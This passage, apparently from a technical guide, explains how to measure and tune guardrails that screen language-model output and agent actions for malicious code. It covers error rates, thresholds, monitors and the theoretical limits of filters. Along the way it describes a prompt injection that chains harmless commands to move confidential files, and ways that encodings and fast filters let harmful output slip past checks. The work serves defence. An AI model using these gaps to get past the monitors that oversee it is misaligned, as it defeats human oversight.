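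A series of allowed actions can still do damage. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of an assistant that can use only `find` and `mv`, which moves files. A prompt injection could make it find confidential documents and move them to a public network drive. Each command is routine, so a check that evaluates them separately would allow both.

Sandboxes have a similar gap because a reviewer at the boundary doesn't see what happens inside, where 93% of the actions in OpenAI's example took place. An agent could add harmful code to a project file without leaving the sandbox, and the developer might later run that file with full permissions. Zed's agent can't request permission to change a project's `.git` folder, because scripts placed there can run outside the sandbox. This rule protects only that folder, but a developer may run almost any file in the project.

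Monitoring works better when it considers earlier actions along with the current one. If an agent writes a script and then runs it, Anthropic's reviewer is supposed to judge the script's contents, and it treats several commands joined on one line as a single action. This still requires judging what the actions do together, and even a perfect monitor can enforce only rules that a program breaks at some identifiable step.

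Keeping valuable things out of the agent's reach is more dependable. In the web version of Claude Code, the real credentials for a user's code repository stay outside the sandbox. The agent gets a substitute with limited permissions, and a proxy checks each request, including which branch it would change, before attaching the real credentials. If the agent runs the criminal's install script there, the script can't steal the real credentials.

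## Measuring false alarms and choosing a threshold

Every check described so far flags some harmless text and misses some malicious code. Making a check stricter usually reduces misses but adds false alarms. To choose a setting, an application's owner needs to know how often each mistake happens, how common malicious code is in the application's traffic, and how much harm each mistake does.

### Three guardrails on the same prompts

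Unit 42's *How Good Are the LLM Guardrails on the Market* compares the built-in guardrails of three large cloud platforms, which it identifies only by number. The researchers used the same language model on each platform, turned on every safety filter at its strictest setting, and finished testing before 10 March 2025.

They used 1,000 harmless prompts, mostly from collections of photography requests, general-knowledge questions, maths problems and Python code. The 123 malicious prompts were jailbreaks, which are prompts written to make a model break its own rules. These are the results for the filters that check a prompt before the model receives it:

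| | Harmless prompts blocked | Code reviews among them | Jailbreaks blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Platform 1 | 1 (0.1%) | 1 | 65 (53%) |
| Platform 2 | 6 (0.6%) | 6 | 112 (91%) |
| Platform 3 | 131 (13.1%) | 25 | 114 (93%) |

Every harmless prompt that Platforms 1 and 2 blocked was a request to review code. One contained an ordinary Python script for charting complex data. Most of Platform 3's other false alarms were maths questions.

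Unit 42 doesn't say how many harmless code-review prompts its test included, so the false positive rate for code review can't be calculated. If they made up a quarter of the harmless set, Platform 2 blocked 6 of 250, or 2.4%, and Platform 3 blocked 10%. If there were only 50, the rates were 12% and 50%. In either case, Platform 2's overall rate of 0.6% underestimates how often it would block harmless prompts to an assistant that mainly serves programmers.

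The study tested the platforms on jailbreaks, not malicious code, so it doesn't show whether any of them would catch the criminal's Acme command. Unit 42 belongs to Palo Alto Networks, which sells its own guardrails. The article is also inconsistent in places. For example, it reports that Platform 1 missed 51 jailbreaks, but blocking 65 of 123 leaves 58. These problems don't affect the main lesson that two products with nearly the same detection rate can differ twentyfold in false alarms.

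### From error rates to precision

Precision, the share of flagged items that are malicious, depends on the base rate as well as on the detector. Let π be the base rate, d the detection rate and f the false positive rate. Out of N messages, πN are malicious and the detector flags dπN of them. The other (1 − π)N are harmless and it flags f(1 − π)N of those. Dividing the correct flags by all the flags gives

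precision = πd / (πd + (1 − π)f)

Suppose an application handles one million messages, of which 100 are malicious. That number is an assumption, and so is using the jailbreak results as detection rates for malicious code. Platform 2 would then catch about 91 of the 100 and wrongly flag 0.6% of the other 999,900, or about 6,000. The same calculation for all three gives:

| | Malicious messages caught | False alarms | Precision |
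|---|---|---|---|
| Platform 1 | 53 | 1,000 | 5.0% |
| Platform 2 | 91 | 6,000 | 1.5% |
| Platform 3 | 93 | 131,000 | 0.07% |

If staff spent two minutes on each false alarm, they would spend 200 hours on Platform 2's and almost 4,400 hours on Platform 3's. Platform 3 would catch about two more malicious messages than Platform 2.

Catching more malicious messages would barely improve Platform 2's precision, which would still be only 1.6% if it caught all 100. For half of its flags to be correct, it could raise at most about 91 false alarms, a false positive rate below 1 in 10,000.

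The assumed base rate matters just as much. *PreAct-Bench* (2026), a test of whether language models can predict harmful behaviour, uses an estimate that 8% of queries in real use are malicious. At that rate, Platform 2's precision would be 93% and Platform 3's 38%. On a test set that is half malicious, Platform 2's precision would be 99%. A vendor could truthfully advertise 99% precision for a product whose alarms are nearly all false in practice.

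The 8% estimate covers malicious queries in general, and malicious code is probably much rarer in most applications. An application's owner can estimate its rate from a random sample, but if 1 in 10,000 messages contains malicious code, a sample of 10,000 would include only one such message on average. Calculating precision for several plausible base rates is more realistic.

### How much traffic contains code

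If most false alarms involve code, their number depends on how much code the application handles. Published figures for the amount of code vary widely, partly because they measure different things.

- According to UNU's *What over 2.5 Billion Daily Messages Reveal About ChatGPT Use*, a summary from the United Nations University, 4.2% of ChatGPT messages concerned programming, in data up to June 2025.
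- Anthropic (2026) found in its March *Economic Index report* that 35% of conversations on its Claude.ai site involved tasks from computing and mathematical occupations.
- A June report by Anthropic (2026) classified Claude conversations by what they produced, and about a sixth produced code or other technical work. This count leaves out Claude Code.
- *State of AI* (2026) covers OpenRouter, a service through which developers reach many companies' models. Programming grew from about 11% of its tokens in early 2025 to more than 50% late in the year.

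The OpenRouter figure overstates programming's share of requests, because programming prompts there are three to four times as long as general ones. If half the tokens are for programming, only about 20% to 25% of the requests are. The ChatGPT figure is probably too low. OpenAI's *Signals individual data*, updated in October 2026, warns that data from personal accounts probably understate technical use because they exclude business customers and Codex.

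Suppose a guardrail wrongly flags 2.4% of harmless messages about code and no other harmless messages. In a million harmless messages, it would raise about 1,000 false alarms if 4.2% of them concern code, 8,400 if 35% do, and 24,000 in an assistant used only for programming. An application's owner should therefore measure the false positive rate for code separately and multiply it by the share of the application's harmless messages that concern code.

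### Building a test set

A test needs at least two collections of harmless text. A random sample of the application's own traffic shows how often ordinary users will get false alarms. A collection of difficult cases shows which kinds of harmless text the detector wrongly flags. The two need separate false alarm rates, because a combined rate would not be accurate for either.

*Comparative Framework Analysis for Enterprise Generative AI Applications* (2026) reports that its guardrail had a precision of 73% and a detection rate of 69% on a test set with deliberately difficult examples. The paper warns against expecting the same rates in production, which would have to be measured on a separate, representative sample. It also recommends reporting precision and detection rate separately instead of as one F1 score, because a false block and a miss have different consequences.

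For a detector of malicious code, the difficult harmless cases should include:

- security lessons, such as one that shows a script tag or explains why `eval()` is dangerous
- incident reports that quote an attacker's commands and addresses
- administration scripts that delete old backups, reset passwords or copy files to another server
- installation guides, including Acme's own

Whether a command should be labeled malicious depends on where it is sent. For example, a report on the Acme attack contains the criminal's command, which would be harmful if someone ran it. The owner will probably want the guardrail to allow that command in a chat response for security staff, but the same command should count as malicious when it is the argument of an agent's tool call. The test set therefore has to record each command's destination as well as its text.

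Real requests from security staff are a good source of difficult cases. *Defensive Refusal Bias* (Campbell, Kale and colleagues, 2026) examined 2,390 prompts from a competition in which student teams defend live computer systems against professional attackers. All of the prompts were legitimate, but three language models refused 12.2% of them on average, with vague or evasive answers counted as refusals. The refusal rate was 43.8% for system hardening (making a system harder to attack), 34.3% for malware analysis and zero for log analysis.

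These were refusals by models from 2024, not by separate guardrails, so the percentages may be out of date, but the patterns are still useful for designing a test. The models refused 30.5% of prompts with words such as "exploit" or "payload", compared with 11.2% of the others. They also refused more often when users said they had permission. A test set could include the same harmless request with and without words like "exploit" to see whether the detector is reacting to vocabulary.

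*Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini* (Kramár, Engels and colleagues, 2026) tests detectors for prompts that seek help with cyberattacks and reports separate error rates for several kinds of text. The harmless test data include ordinary traffic, short prompts that resemble attacks, conversations with several turns, and very long prompts. Detectors trained on short prompts did poorly on long ones, which an average over mostly short prompts could easily have hidden. A text guardrail needs a similar test with long answers that contain one command in the middle of a sentence.

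The test should run complete messages through the whole guardrail. If code extraction finds 90% of malicious snippets and the classifier flags 90% of those, the guardrail catches 81%. Testing the classifier alone on already extracted snippets would give a rate of 90%, because it leaves out the snippets that extraction missed.

Results for different kinds of text can then be combined according to their share of real traffic. Suppose 2% of harmless messages are difficult cases and the detector flags 10% of them, along with 0.1% of the rest:

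0.02 × 10% + 0.98 × 0.1% ≈ 0.3%

Difficult cases would then cause about two thirds of the false alarms, so improving the detector on them would help more than any improvement on ordinary cases.

### What a clean result proves

Suppose a detector flags none of 1,000 harmless messages. If its true false positive rate is f, the probability of that result is (1 − f)¹⁰⁰⁰. This falls to 5% when

f = 1 − 0.05^(1/1000) ≈ 0.3%

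The test therefore shows, at 95% confidence, only that the rate is below about 0.3%. A detector with a rate of 0.3% would still raise 3,000 false alarms in a million harmless messages. When a test of n harmless messages produces no false alarms, the 95% upper limit on the rate is about 3/n. To establish a rate below 1 in 10,000, the owner would need to test about 30,000 harmless messages without a false alarm.

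A false-alarm rate estimated from only a few errors is also uncertain. Platform 1 raised one false alarm in 1,000, which is compatible with a true rate from almost zero to about 0.56%. Platform 2 raised six, which is compatible with a rate from about 0.2% to 1.3%. These ranges overlap, so the study is weak evidence that Platform 1 raises fewer false alarms than Platform 2, but it leaves no real doubt that Platform 3 raises more than either.

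The 3/n approximation assumes that the test messages are independent samples of the traffic. According to Anthropic, the test in which none of 720 prompt injections succeeded against Claude Code's auto mode consisted of 72 scenarios run ten times each. Treating all 720 attempts as independent gives an upper limit of 0.4% on the success rate. If repeated attempts at a scenario nearly always end the same way, the limit is closer to 3/72, or 4%.

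### Setting a threshold from costs

To choose a threshold, the owner needs a detector that gives scores. A language-model judge may answer only "safe" or "unsafe", but it assigns a probability to each possible first word before writing one. *TWGuard* (2026) uses these probabilities as scores. If a judge gives "unsafe" a 30% chance and "safe" 70%, it will normally answer "safe", but a 20% threshold would still flag the message.

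If the score were the true probability p that a message is malicious, the best threshold would follow directly from the costs. Flagging is worthwhile when the expected cost of letting the message through is higher than the expected cost of stopping it:

p × C_miss > (1 − p) × C_false

which means

p > C_false / (C_false + C_miss)

If a false alarm costs $5 and a miss costs $10,000, the threshold for flagging a message is a 0.05% chance, or 1 in 2,000, that it is malicious. A precision of 1.5% may therefore be acceptable if each false alarm costs that little. But false alarms can cost more as they accumulate, because a reviewer who sees 66 for every real attack may stop reading carefully.

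Raw scores are rarely accurate enough for this formula. *Safety-Flag* (2026) found that the average gap between confidence and actual accuracy ranged from 8 to 18 percentage points for four specialised guard models. Even an 8-point error makes a threshold of 0.05% meaningless. These models moderate harmful content in general, but there is little reason to expect detectors of malicious code to do much better.

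Scores also depend on the base rate in the data used to calibrate them. Suppose a score of 99%, or odds of 99 to 1, is correct for a test set in which half the messages are malicious. In traffic with one malicious message in 10,000, the same score corresponds to odds of 99 to 9,999, or a probability of about 1%.

A safer method is to try several thresholds on labelled data, measure d and f at each, and compare the expected cost per message:

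cost = π(1 − d) × C_miss + (1 − π)f × C_false

The three platforms can represent three thresholds. With 100 malicious messages in a million, moving from Platform 1 to Platform 2 catches 38 more of them and adds 5,000 false alarms. That is worthwhile if a miss is at least 131 times as bad as a false alarm. Moving to Platform 3 is worthwhile only if a miss is about 77,000 times as bad, which is hard to imagine for a chat assistant.

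Estimates of the harm from a miss should take account of other protections. In Unit 42's test, the underlying model itself refused 109 of the 123 jailbreaks, so most of those that got past a filter would have done no harm. A missed malicious command also does less damage if it runs in a sandbox with nothing valuable inside. An owner who assumes that every miss does as much damage as a successful attack will set the threshold too strictly.

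Many owners can't put a credible price on a miss, but they can limit the false alarm rate and accept whatever detection rate results. In *Constitutional Classifiers++*, Cunningham, Wei and colleagues (2026) test Anthropic's classifiers, which guard against requests for help with weapons such as chemical and biological ones. They often set the threshold so that a classifier flagged 0.1% of a public collection of chatbot conversations. To apply the same limit to 100,000 harmless messages, an owner would sort the scores and place the threshold just below the 100th highest. With only 1,000 messages, the threshold would depend on a single message.

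Whichever method the owner uses, the final error rates have to come from data that was not used to choose the threshold. Otherwise, the threshold will partly fit chance features of one sample and look better than it is. Kramár and colleagues choose their threshold on one dataset by minimising a weighted sum of errors, with the most weight on false alarms, and report results on a different kind of dataset.

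Comparing products at their default thresholds can also mislead. In *Safety-Flag*'s results, ShieldGemma flagged 3.8% of harmless items and missed 50.2% of harmful ones, while WildGuard flagged 13.1% and missed 10.9%. Some of that difference may only reflect WildGuard's stricter default. A fair comparison would set both thresholds to give the same false positive rate, then compare detection rates.

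### A cheap check followed by a slower one

Running two checks in sequence can reduce both false alarms and computing costs. The first check examines everything and passes what it flags to the second, which makes the final decision. A harmless message is blocked only if both checks flag it, but a malicious message gets through if either check misses it. If d₂ and f₂ are the second check's rates on what it receives, the combined rates are

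d = d₁ × d₂ and f = f₁ × f₂

In Claude Code's auto mode, the second check cleared about 95% of the first check's false alarms, but it also cleared about 11% of the dangerous actions the first had caught. If 100 in every million actions were dangerous, the second check would raise precision from about 0.1% to 2%.

Testing the second check on ordinary text gives misleading rates, because that check receives only what the first check found suspicious, which is harder to judge. Two checks that each flag 1% of harmless messages will both flag 1 in 10,000 only if their mistakes are independent. If both react to the word "payload", the combined rate could be close to 1%.

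The computing cost per message is

c₁ + q × c₂

where q is the share that the first check passes on. In an early version of Anthropic's system, the first classifier cost about a third as much as the second and passed on about 10% of the traffic. The total was therefore 0.33 + 0.10 = 0.43 times the cost of running the second classifier on everything, and more than three quarters of it went on the first.

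Cunningham and colleagues then replaced the first classifier with a probe, a small classifier that uses the numbers the protected model computes internally as it processes text. The model already computes these numbers, so the probe adds almost no computation. It sent 5.5% of real traffic to the second stage, and computation fell by a factor of about eight, as the formula predicts. The complete system needed about one-fortieth of the computation of the team's original single classifier, partly because the second stage used a newer, more efficient model.

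The final system refused 0.05% of real traffic, compared with 0.038% for the original single classifier, so its main gains were in cost and resistance to attack. Some of the refusals were presumably correct. Using a probe requires access to a model's internals, but a rule or an n-gram classifier could replace it as the step before a language-model judge.

A first check can also handle the clearest cases on its own. Kramár and colleagues use two thresholds. They pass prompts that score below the lower one, flag those that score above the upper one, and send only the rest to a language model. Sending 8% of prompts to the language model gave a lower error rate than using either the first check or the language model alone, although the margins of error were wide.

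Blocking every message that any of several checks flags increases false alarms. Five independent checks with a false positive rate of 0.5% each would together flag about 2.5% of harmless messages. Switching on every available rule set increases false alarms in the same way.

### What to do with a flagged message

The cost of a false alarm depends on what the guardrail does next.

| Response | Effect on a real attack | Cost of a false alarm |
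|---|---|---|
| Log it | The attack continues, but staff can find it later | A reviewer's time |
| Ask a person | Stops the attack if the person refuses | An interruption, and less attention to later questions |
| Remove the snippet | Stops the attack if extraction found all the code | A gap in an otherwise useful answer |
| Block the message or action | Stops the attack | A lost answer, or an agent that has to find another way |

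Logging is the right way to introduce a new check. Cunningham and colleagues ran their check on real traffic in a month-long "shadow deployment" and estimated its refusal rate before users depended on it. Logging alone is a poor response to a command that an agent is about to run, because staff may not read the entry until long after the damage is done.

Asking a person for approval works best when they have information that the guardrail lacks, such as whether they meant to install Acme, but it adds little as a general safeguard. In Anthropic's experiment with paid testers, people refused only six dangerous commands that auto mode had allowed, so adding their refusals would have raised the share of dangerous commands stopped from 89.0% to 89.6%.

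Removing the flagged snippet suits long answers that people read. The application should put a visible notice in its place, so that readers don't try to follow instructions with a step missing. Databricks, for example, lets customers of its AI gateway block flagged content or sanitise it.

Blocking makes the most sense just before code runs, but the agent needs a way to continue afterward. At a false positive rate of 0.4% per action, an agent that takes 200 checked actions has a 55% chance of at least one wrongful block, if the errors are independent. Ending the session after every block would make long tasks impractical. Auto mode gives the agent the reason for the block and instructs it to look for a safer approach. After three blocks in a row or 20 in total, it hands over to the user, or ends the session if nobody is there. According to Anthropic, a false alarm then usually leads to just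 one retry.

An application can use several of these responses, each with its own threshold. If a false alarm costs 10 cents when the guardrail only logs a message and $5 when it blocks one, the cost formula justifies logging at a much lower score than blocking. If the address in the criminal's Acme command looks slightly suspicious, a chat application might only log the command. The same score on an agent's tool call could justify holding the command until the guardrail has fetched and inspected the script.

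## What no text checker can guarantee

All the detectors in the published tests make mistakes. A proof shows that no checker, including a language model, can read every possible program and always determine correctly whether running it would do harm. However, the proof has conditions that matter a great deal for a real guardrail.

### The halting problem

A yes-or-no question about programs is decidable if some procedure always finishes and gives the right answer for every program. Otherwise, it is undecidable, although many individual cases may still be easy. The best-known example is whether a program will eventually stop. This is called the halting problem, and Alan Turing proved it undecidable in the 1930s.

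Evans's *On the Impossibility of Virus Detection* explains why two obvious ways to check whether a program will ever stop fail. One is to run the program and wait. This works if the program stops, but a program still running after a million steps may stop at step 1,000,001, so the checker can never safely answer "no". The other is to watch for an exact repeat of an earlier state, since a program that returns to the same state will repeat forever. But a program can also run forever without repeating a state, for example by counting upwards.

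Every other approach fails too. Suppose a program called HALTS always predicts correctly whether a program will stop. Someone could then write a program called CONTRARY that runs HALTS on CONTRARY's own text, loops forever if HALTS predicts that CONTRARY will stop, and stops if HALTS predicts that it will run forever. HALTS is wrong either way, so no such program can exist.

### From stopping to doing harm

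The same limit applies to malicious code. Take any program P and build a new program with two steps:

1. Run P on temporary copies of the computer's files, with no way to affect anything real.
2. When P ends, delete the user's files.

For any program P, someone could build a new program that does harm if P ends and does nothing harmful if P runs forever. A perfect malware checker could examine the new program without running it, and its verdict would show whether P ends. The checker would then solve the halting problem, which no program can do, so no perfect malware checker exists.

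The temporary copies are needed because P might itself delete files and then run forever. Without them, the checker would correctly label the new program malicious, and someone could wrongly conclude that P ends. Evans gives the same proof with a virus as the harmful step.

The argument works equally well if the second step sends an email or displays a picture instead of deleting files. Henry Gordon Rice proved the general result in 1951. Rice's theorem states that every property of what programs do is undecidable, unless all programs have the property or none do. The theorem does not cover properties of a program's text. Anyone can check whether a script contains the word `curl`, but no procedure can determine for every script whether it will ever contact the network.

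In *Cure of Computer Viruses*, Cohen (1984) used a program like CONTRARY to prove the result for viruses. Cohen's program runs a supposedly perfect virus detector on itself and infects other programs only if the detector finds no virus. Cohen adds that a detector can be built to catch any particular virus, but every detector has some virus that can get past it. A defender can therefore write a rule for each past attack, but not one rule that catches all future attacks.

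The journal version of *Computer Viruses* (Cohen, 1987) argues that there is no fundamental distinction between data and programs, because "information only has meaning in its interpretation." Similarly, `{{7*7}}` is text in a chat window but a calculation in a template engine. Cohen also points out that a virus can't spread in a system that can only display files, because such a system can't modify them. A chat page that properly encodes each response before displaying it has much the same protection.

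### Confirming harm is easier than confirming safety

*No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (Pérez-Acle, 2026) considers a gatekeeper that reads programs written by an AI and decides which may run. The gatekeeper can confirm every violation of a ban by running the program until it does the forbidden thing, but it can't confirm that every safe program is safe, because however long a program has run without harm, its next step might be harmful.

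One of Pérez-Acle's examples is a program that checks the even numbers from 4 upwards and does something forbidden if it finds one that isn't the sum of two primes. Goldbach's conjecture, an open problem as of November 2026, holds that no such number exists. The program is short and readable, but nobody could certify it as safe without proving the conjecture. Pérez-Acle ran it for a million steps and nothing happened, but that proves very little about whether it is safe.

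This is why a harmful action in a sandbox test is much stronger evidence than a quiet run, however long the run lasts.

Rules about secrets are even harder to check. Suppose a program's published output must not depend on a password. A checker could run the program with two different passwords and compare the outputs. But if one run has published a word and the other nothing, the second may be about to publish the same word, so the checker can't yet tell whether the password has leaked. In Pérez-Acle's model, where only the published sequence matters, not its timing, no procedure can confirm every leak or every safe program.

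A time limit makes these questions decidable, since the checker can run the program until the limit. But Pérez-Acle proves that a checker that is always right must take about as long on some programs as running them would. A checker that is much faster than a sandbox on every program must therefore sometimes make a mistake or answer "unknown".

Pérez-Acle generated 2.2 million small random programs to see how often the difficulty arises, and 1.6% of them did the forbidden action. An eight-step test missed 30% of the unsafe programs among the longest ones, but a 128-step test missed none at any length. Pérez-Acle concludes that the difficulty comes from programs written to defeat a checker, not from typical ones. The conclusion is plausible, but the experiment is weak evidence for it because random instructions resemble neither ordinary software nor malware. The error counts also exclude programs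 whose long-run behaviour remained unresolved, which may be the hardest ones.

### Filters that judge meaning

*LLM Censorship* (Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues, 2023) applies Rice's theorem to language models. If a provider permits some program behaviours and forbids others, no algorithm can determine from every program description whether the program is permitted. This applies to both prompts and responses.

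They also prove a theorem about filters that judge the meaning of a response, which holds even if responses have a maximum length. The theorem assumes that the model can apply any reversible encoding a user describes, and that an encoded version of a forbidden text is also forbidden if the recipient knows how to decode it.

For any forbidden text and any permitted one, some reversible encoding turns the first into the second. A filter with no information about which encodings the recipient can reverse must therefore block the permitted text too, because it could be the forbidden text in encoded form. The same reasoning applies to every other permitted text, so the filter must permit everything or nothing.

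This standard is very demanding, because under it "Good morning" might be an encoded password stealer. In practice, the model has to encode the program accurately and the recipient has to know how to decode it. Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge that the theorem doesn't cover filters that examine the prompt and response together, and the prompt may well contain the encoding instructions.

The theorem also matters little when the recipient is a known program. A database runs the SQL it receives and doesn't decode a greeting into a query. The theorem is therefore a much bigger problem for a general chat assistant, whose users may know any decoding scheme, than for the sales dashboard.

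Glukhov and colleagues conclude that providers should treat the problem as one of computer security instead of relying on better classifiers. They suggest controlling which tools and data an untrusted input can affect. This is good advice for malicious code, because limits on access still work when a filter misclassifies the text.

### When a perfect checker exists

*No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (Amer, Kinczel and Long, 2026) defines a policy as a set of forbidden outputs, and an exact checker as one that blocks every forbidden output and passes every permitted one. It shows that if a model can produce every finite string, an exact checker exists if and only if the policy is decidable.

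An exact checker exists if and only if some procedure can decide the policy. Any such procedure can serve as the checker. Conversely, an exact checker could be used to decide the policy for any string, by searching for a prompt that can produce the string and submitting both to the checker.

A checker can exactly enforce a ban on a list of phrases, but no checker can exactly enforce a ban on programs that will ever take some harmful action, because that property is undecidable. Every checker for such a ban is wrong about infinitely many outputs, and one that never lets a forbidden output through must also block infinitely many permitted ones.

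Amer and colleagues prove that even a checker that makes random choices will be wrong at least half the time on some output. A majority vote among several language-model judges can reduce ordinary errors, but it can't remove this limit. The result holds even if the model can't produce every string, as long as it can produce all the programs needed for a proof like the one with P.

A monitor has an easier task because it sees each action just before it happens and doesn't have to predict anything. If the policy is a list of forbidden actions, the monitor only has to compare the next action with the list. Amer and colleagues prove that such a monitor prevents every forbidden action and never stops a program that doesn't attempt one. This works only if the monitor can recognise the actions on the list, and can see and stop every action the program attempts.

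For example, a sandbox's proxy can exactly enforce its list of allowed domains if all connections go through it. But the list can still be wrong, as with Acme's lapsed domain.

The guarantee also fails when an ordinary action delivers something harmful. Writing a file is usually harmless, but the file may contain a program that someone will run later. If the rule forbids writing malicious programs, the monitor has to judge the file's contents, and the problem is undecidable again. A monitor on the computer where the program runs could still stop its forbidden actions.

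*What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) gives the example of an assistant that can send emails and payments. A check before each action can exactly enforce a daily limit on payments to each recipient, because it only has to add up the amounts. But a rule against emailing personal data to unapproved recipients requires someone or something to judge what counts as personal data, and some of those judgements will be wrong.

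Ray shows that the information available to a judge limits how well it can trade off wrongful blocks against misses. Combining several judges can't overcome this limit if they all use the same information. Detection of malicious code is usually limited in this way, so showing a judge the script that a command downloads is likely to help more than asking another judge about the command.

### Fast filters and a cryptographic assumption

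A guardrail also has to be fast enough to use. *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025), accepted for the 2026 ICLR machine-learning conference, proves limits on efficient filters. Its main results assume the existence of time-lock puzzles, which are quick to create but take at least a set amount of computing time to solve. Cryptographers proposed a way to make them in 1996, but the method's security depends on the unproved assumption that a certain long calculation has no shortcut.

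Under that assumption, for some language models, no prompt filter that runs significantly faster than the model can distinguish certain harmful prompts from innocent ones. A similar result holds for responses. For any language model, there is another with a similar running time, and a measure of harm, such that no efficient filter can distinguish the second model's harmful responses from the first model's responses, even if the filter runs for longer than the model.

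These theorems show that such models exist, but not that anyone has deployed one. Ball and colleagues acknowledge that the model in their main proof may behave in a contrived way, but argue that attackers have exploited seemingly contrived weaknesses before. They cite the theft of more than $60 million from programs on the Ethereum blockchain in 2016. That is a fair reason for caution, but one case from another field is weak evidence of how likely such an attack on a language model is.

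The condition on speed is the most useful part for a defender. A fast filter in front of a much more powerful model can't be guaranteed in general to recognise everything the model can act on, which is a good reason to check responses and actions too. The prompt theorem doesn't cover probes like Anthropic's, because they aren't separate, faster programs.

Ball and colleagues conclude that filters outside a model can't make it safe. For malicious code, this conclusion applies only to filters on text. These theorems don't rule out a monitor, also outside the model, that enforces a ban on particular actions.

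### Limited lengths and restricted programs

Real models can't produce every finite string, because their responses have a maximum length. Only finitely many responses can then be forbidden, and a table could in principle list them all. Amer and colleagues point out that an exact checker therefore exists for any fixed maximum length.

Nobody could write out such a table, though, because 95 printable characters can form more than 10⁸¹ strings of 41 characters, the length of the Acme command. Limiting a program's length also doesn't limit how long it runs. The Goldbach program fits in a few lines, and the correct table must mark it either "allow" or "block", but nobody knows which. Amer and colleagues prove that, for an undecidable policy, no single procedure can produce the correct checker for every length limit. They caution that this doesn't rule out a practical exact checker for a particular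 system.

A real computer has finite memory, so every program on it must eventually stop or repeat an earlier state. Evans's example, a cheap computer with 16 kilobytes of memory, has 2 to the power of 131,072 possible states, a number with more than 39,000 digits (Evans mistakenly gives 81). Waiting for a repeat could take far longer than the age of the universe.

Restricting programs is more practical, but only if the restriction limits what they can compute. Requiring every script to be in Python, with a comment above each function, makes scripts easier to read but leaves the question undecidable. The checker can settle the question by running the program if every permitted program must finish within a number of steps that can be worked out from its text. Banning loops and functions that call themselves can ensure this, if the ban also covers every other way of repeating or running code.

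Pérez-Acle lists several systems that give up some generality in this way. Linux has a verifier for eBPF programs, which are small extensions to the core of the operating system. It accepts only programs that it can prove safe, so it also rejects some safe ones. Ethereum charges for each step of a program, so every transaction has a limited budget. With proof-carrying code, the author supplies a proof of safety with the program, and the recipient only has to check it.

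These methods suit small programs with narrow jobs, but a coding agent that could write only loop-free scripts would be of little use.

The wording of a rule can also make it easier to check. Pérez-Acle recommends rules that require a program to do something visible, such as recording a request before changing any data. A finite record can confirm that the program did this, but not that it will never do something else.

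### No minimum average error

These theorems count the strings that a checker gets wrong. All of those strings could be extremely rare, so the theorems do not imply that guardrails must have high error rates.

Amer and colleagues prove that for any fixed distribution of outputs and any target rate above zero, some checker blocks every forbidden output and wrongly blocks permitted ones at less than the target rate. Such a checker can use a finite table large enough to cover nearly all the traffic, and block everything outside it. There is no general method for building the table, so the proof doesn't give developers a way to reach the target. But it means that undecidability doesn't justify a false positive rate of 5%, and that a measured rate of 0.05% is consistent with the theory.

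### What rare attacks can cost

Good average performance can still leave a large loss, because attackers choose what to send. Amer and colleagues give a simple lower bound. Let α be the share of uses that are hostile, σ the probability that a hostile use gets a forbidden output past the checker, and λ the smallest loss from such an output. If no use has a negative loss, then

expected loss per use ≥ α × σ × λ

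Suppose that 0.1% of uses are hostile, 5% of those succeed, and each success costs at least $10,000. These numbers are invented, but they give

0.001 × 0.05 × $10,000 = $0.50

The expected loss is at least 50 cents per use, or $500,000 per million uses. But only one use in 20,000 involves a successful attack, so the checker would look excellent if its results were averaged over all uses.

The 5% success rate shouldn't come from a fixed test set alone, because attackers will repeat whatever works. If their success rate rises to 50%, the bound rises to $5 per use.

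The formula also helps in comparing defences. If each successful attack costs $10,000, a stricter checker that cuts the success rate from 5% to 1% reduces the average loss per use from 50 cents to 10 cents. At $5 per false alarm, the 40-cent saving would justify extra false alarms on up to 8% of uses. Running the code in a sandbox where an attack can do only $100 of damage would reduce the loss to half a cent, even with the original checker.

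This bound applies whenever the checker in use lets some attacks through, even if a perfect checker for the policy exists, so it does not depend on undecidability.

### Theory, missing information and engineering

Few of the errors that guardrails make in published tests are related to Rice's theorem. Some come from missing information. For example, even a checker with unlimited computing power couldn't reliably distinguish the two Acme commands by their text alone. Others come from ordinary defects that developers can fix.

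| Difficulty | Main cause | What can help |
|---|---|---|
| No checker is right about every possible program | Theory | Limit what programs can compute, or accept some errors |
| A clean sandbox run doesn't prove that a program is safe | Theory, unless the program is restricted | Keep limits in place when the program runs for real |
| A fast check can't always be right | Theory, in the worst case | Allow the answer "unknown" |
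| The two Acme commands look alike | Missing information | Inspect the script and find out who owns the domain |
| A backup program and a thief may send the same files | Missing information about what the owner wants | Pass the user's request to the checker |
| An extractor misses a command in a sentence | Engineering | Search the prose as well as the marked code |
| A judge blocks a well-known installer | Engineering, and sometimes missing information | Improve the instructions and test on similar harmless cases |
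| A monitor doesn't see some network connections | Engineering | Route all connections through the monitor |

Nobody can honestly promise that a guardrail will block all malicious code and allow all harmless code if the programs are unrestricted. Amer and colleagues recommend that a rule about the meaning or effect of text specify a tolerated error rate, the kind of use it applies to, and the kind of attacker. A company buying a guardrail could, for example, require a false positive rate below 0.1% on its own traffic and a detection rate above 95% on an agreed set of attacks. For a rule about specified actions, such as a ban on connections to unlisted domains, the company could require exact enforcement.
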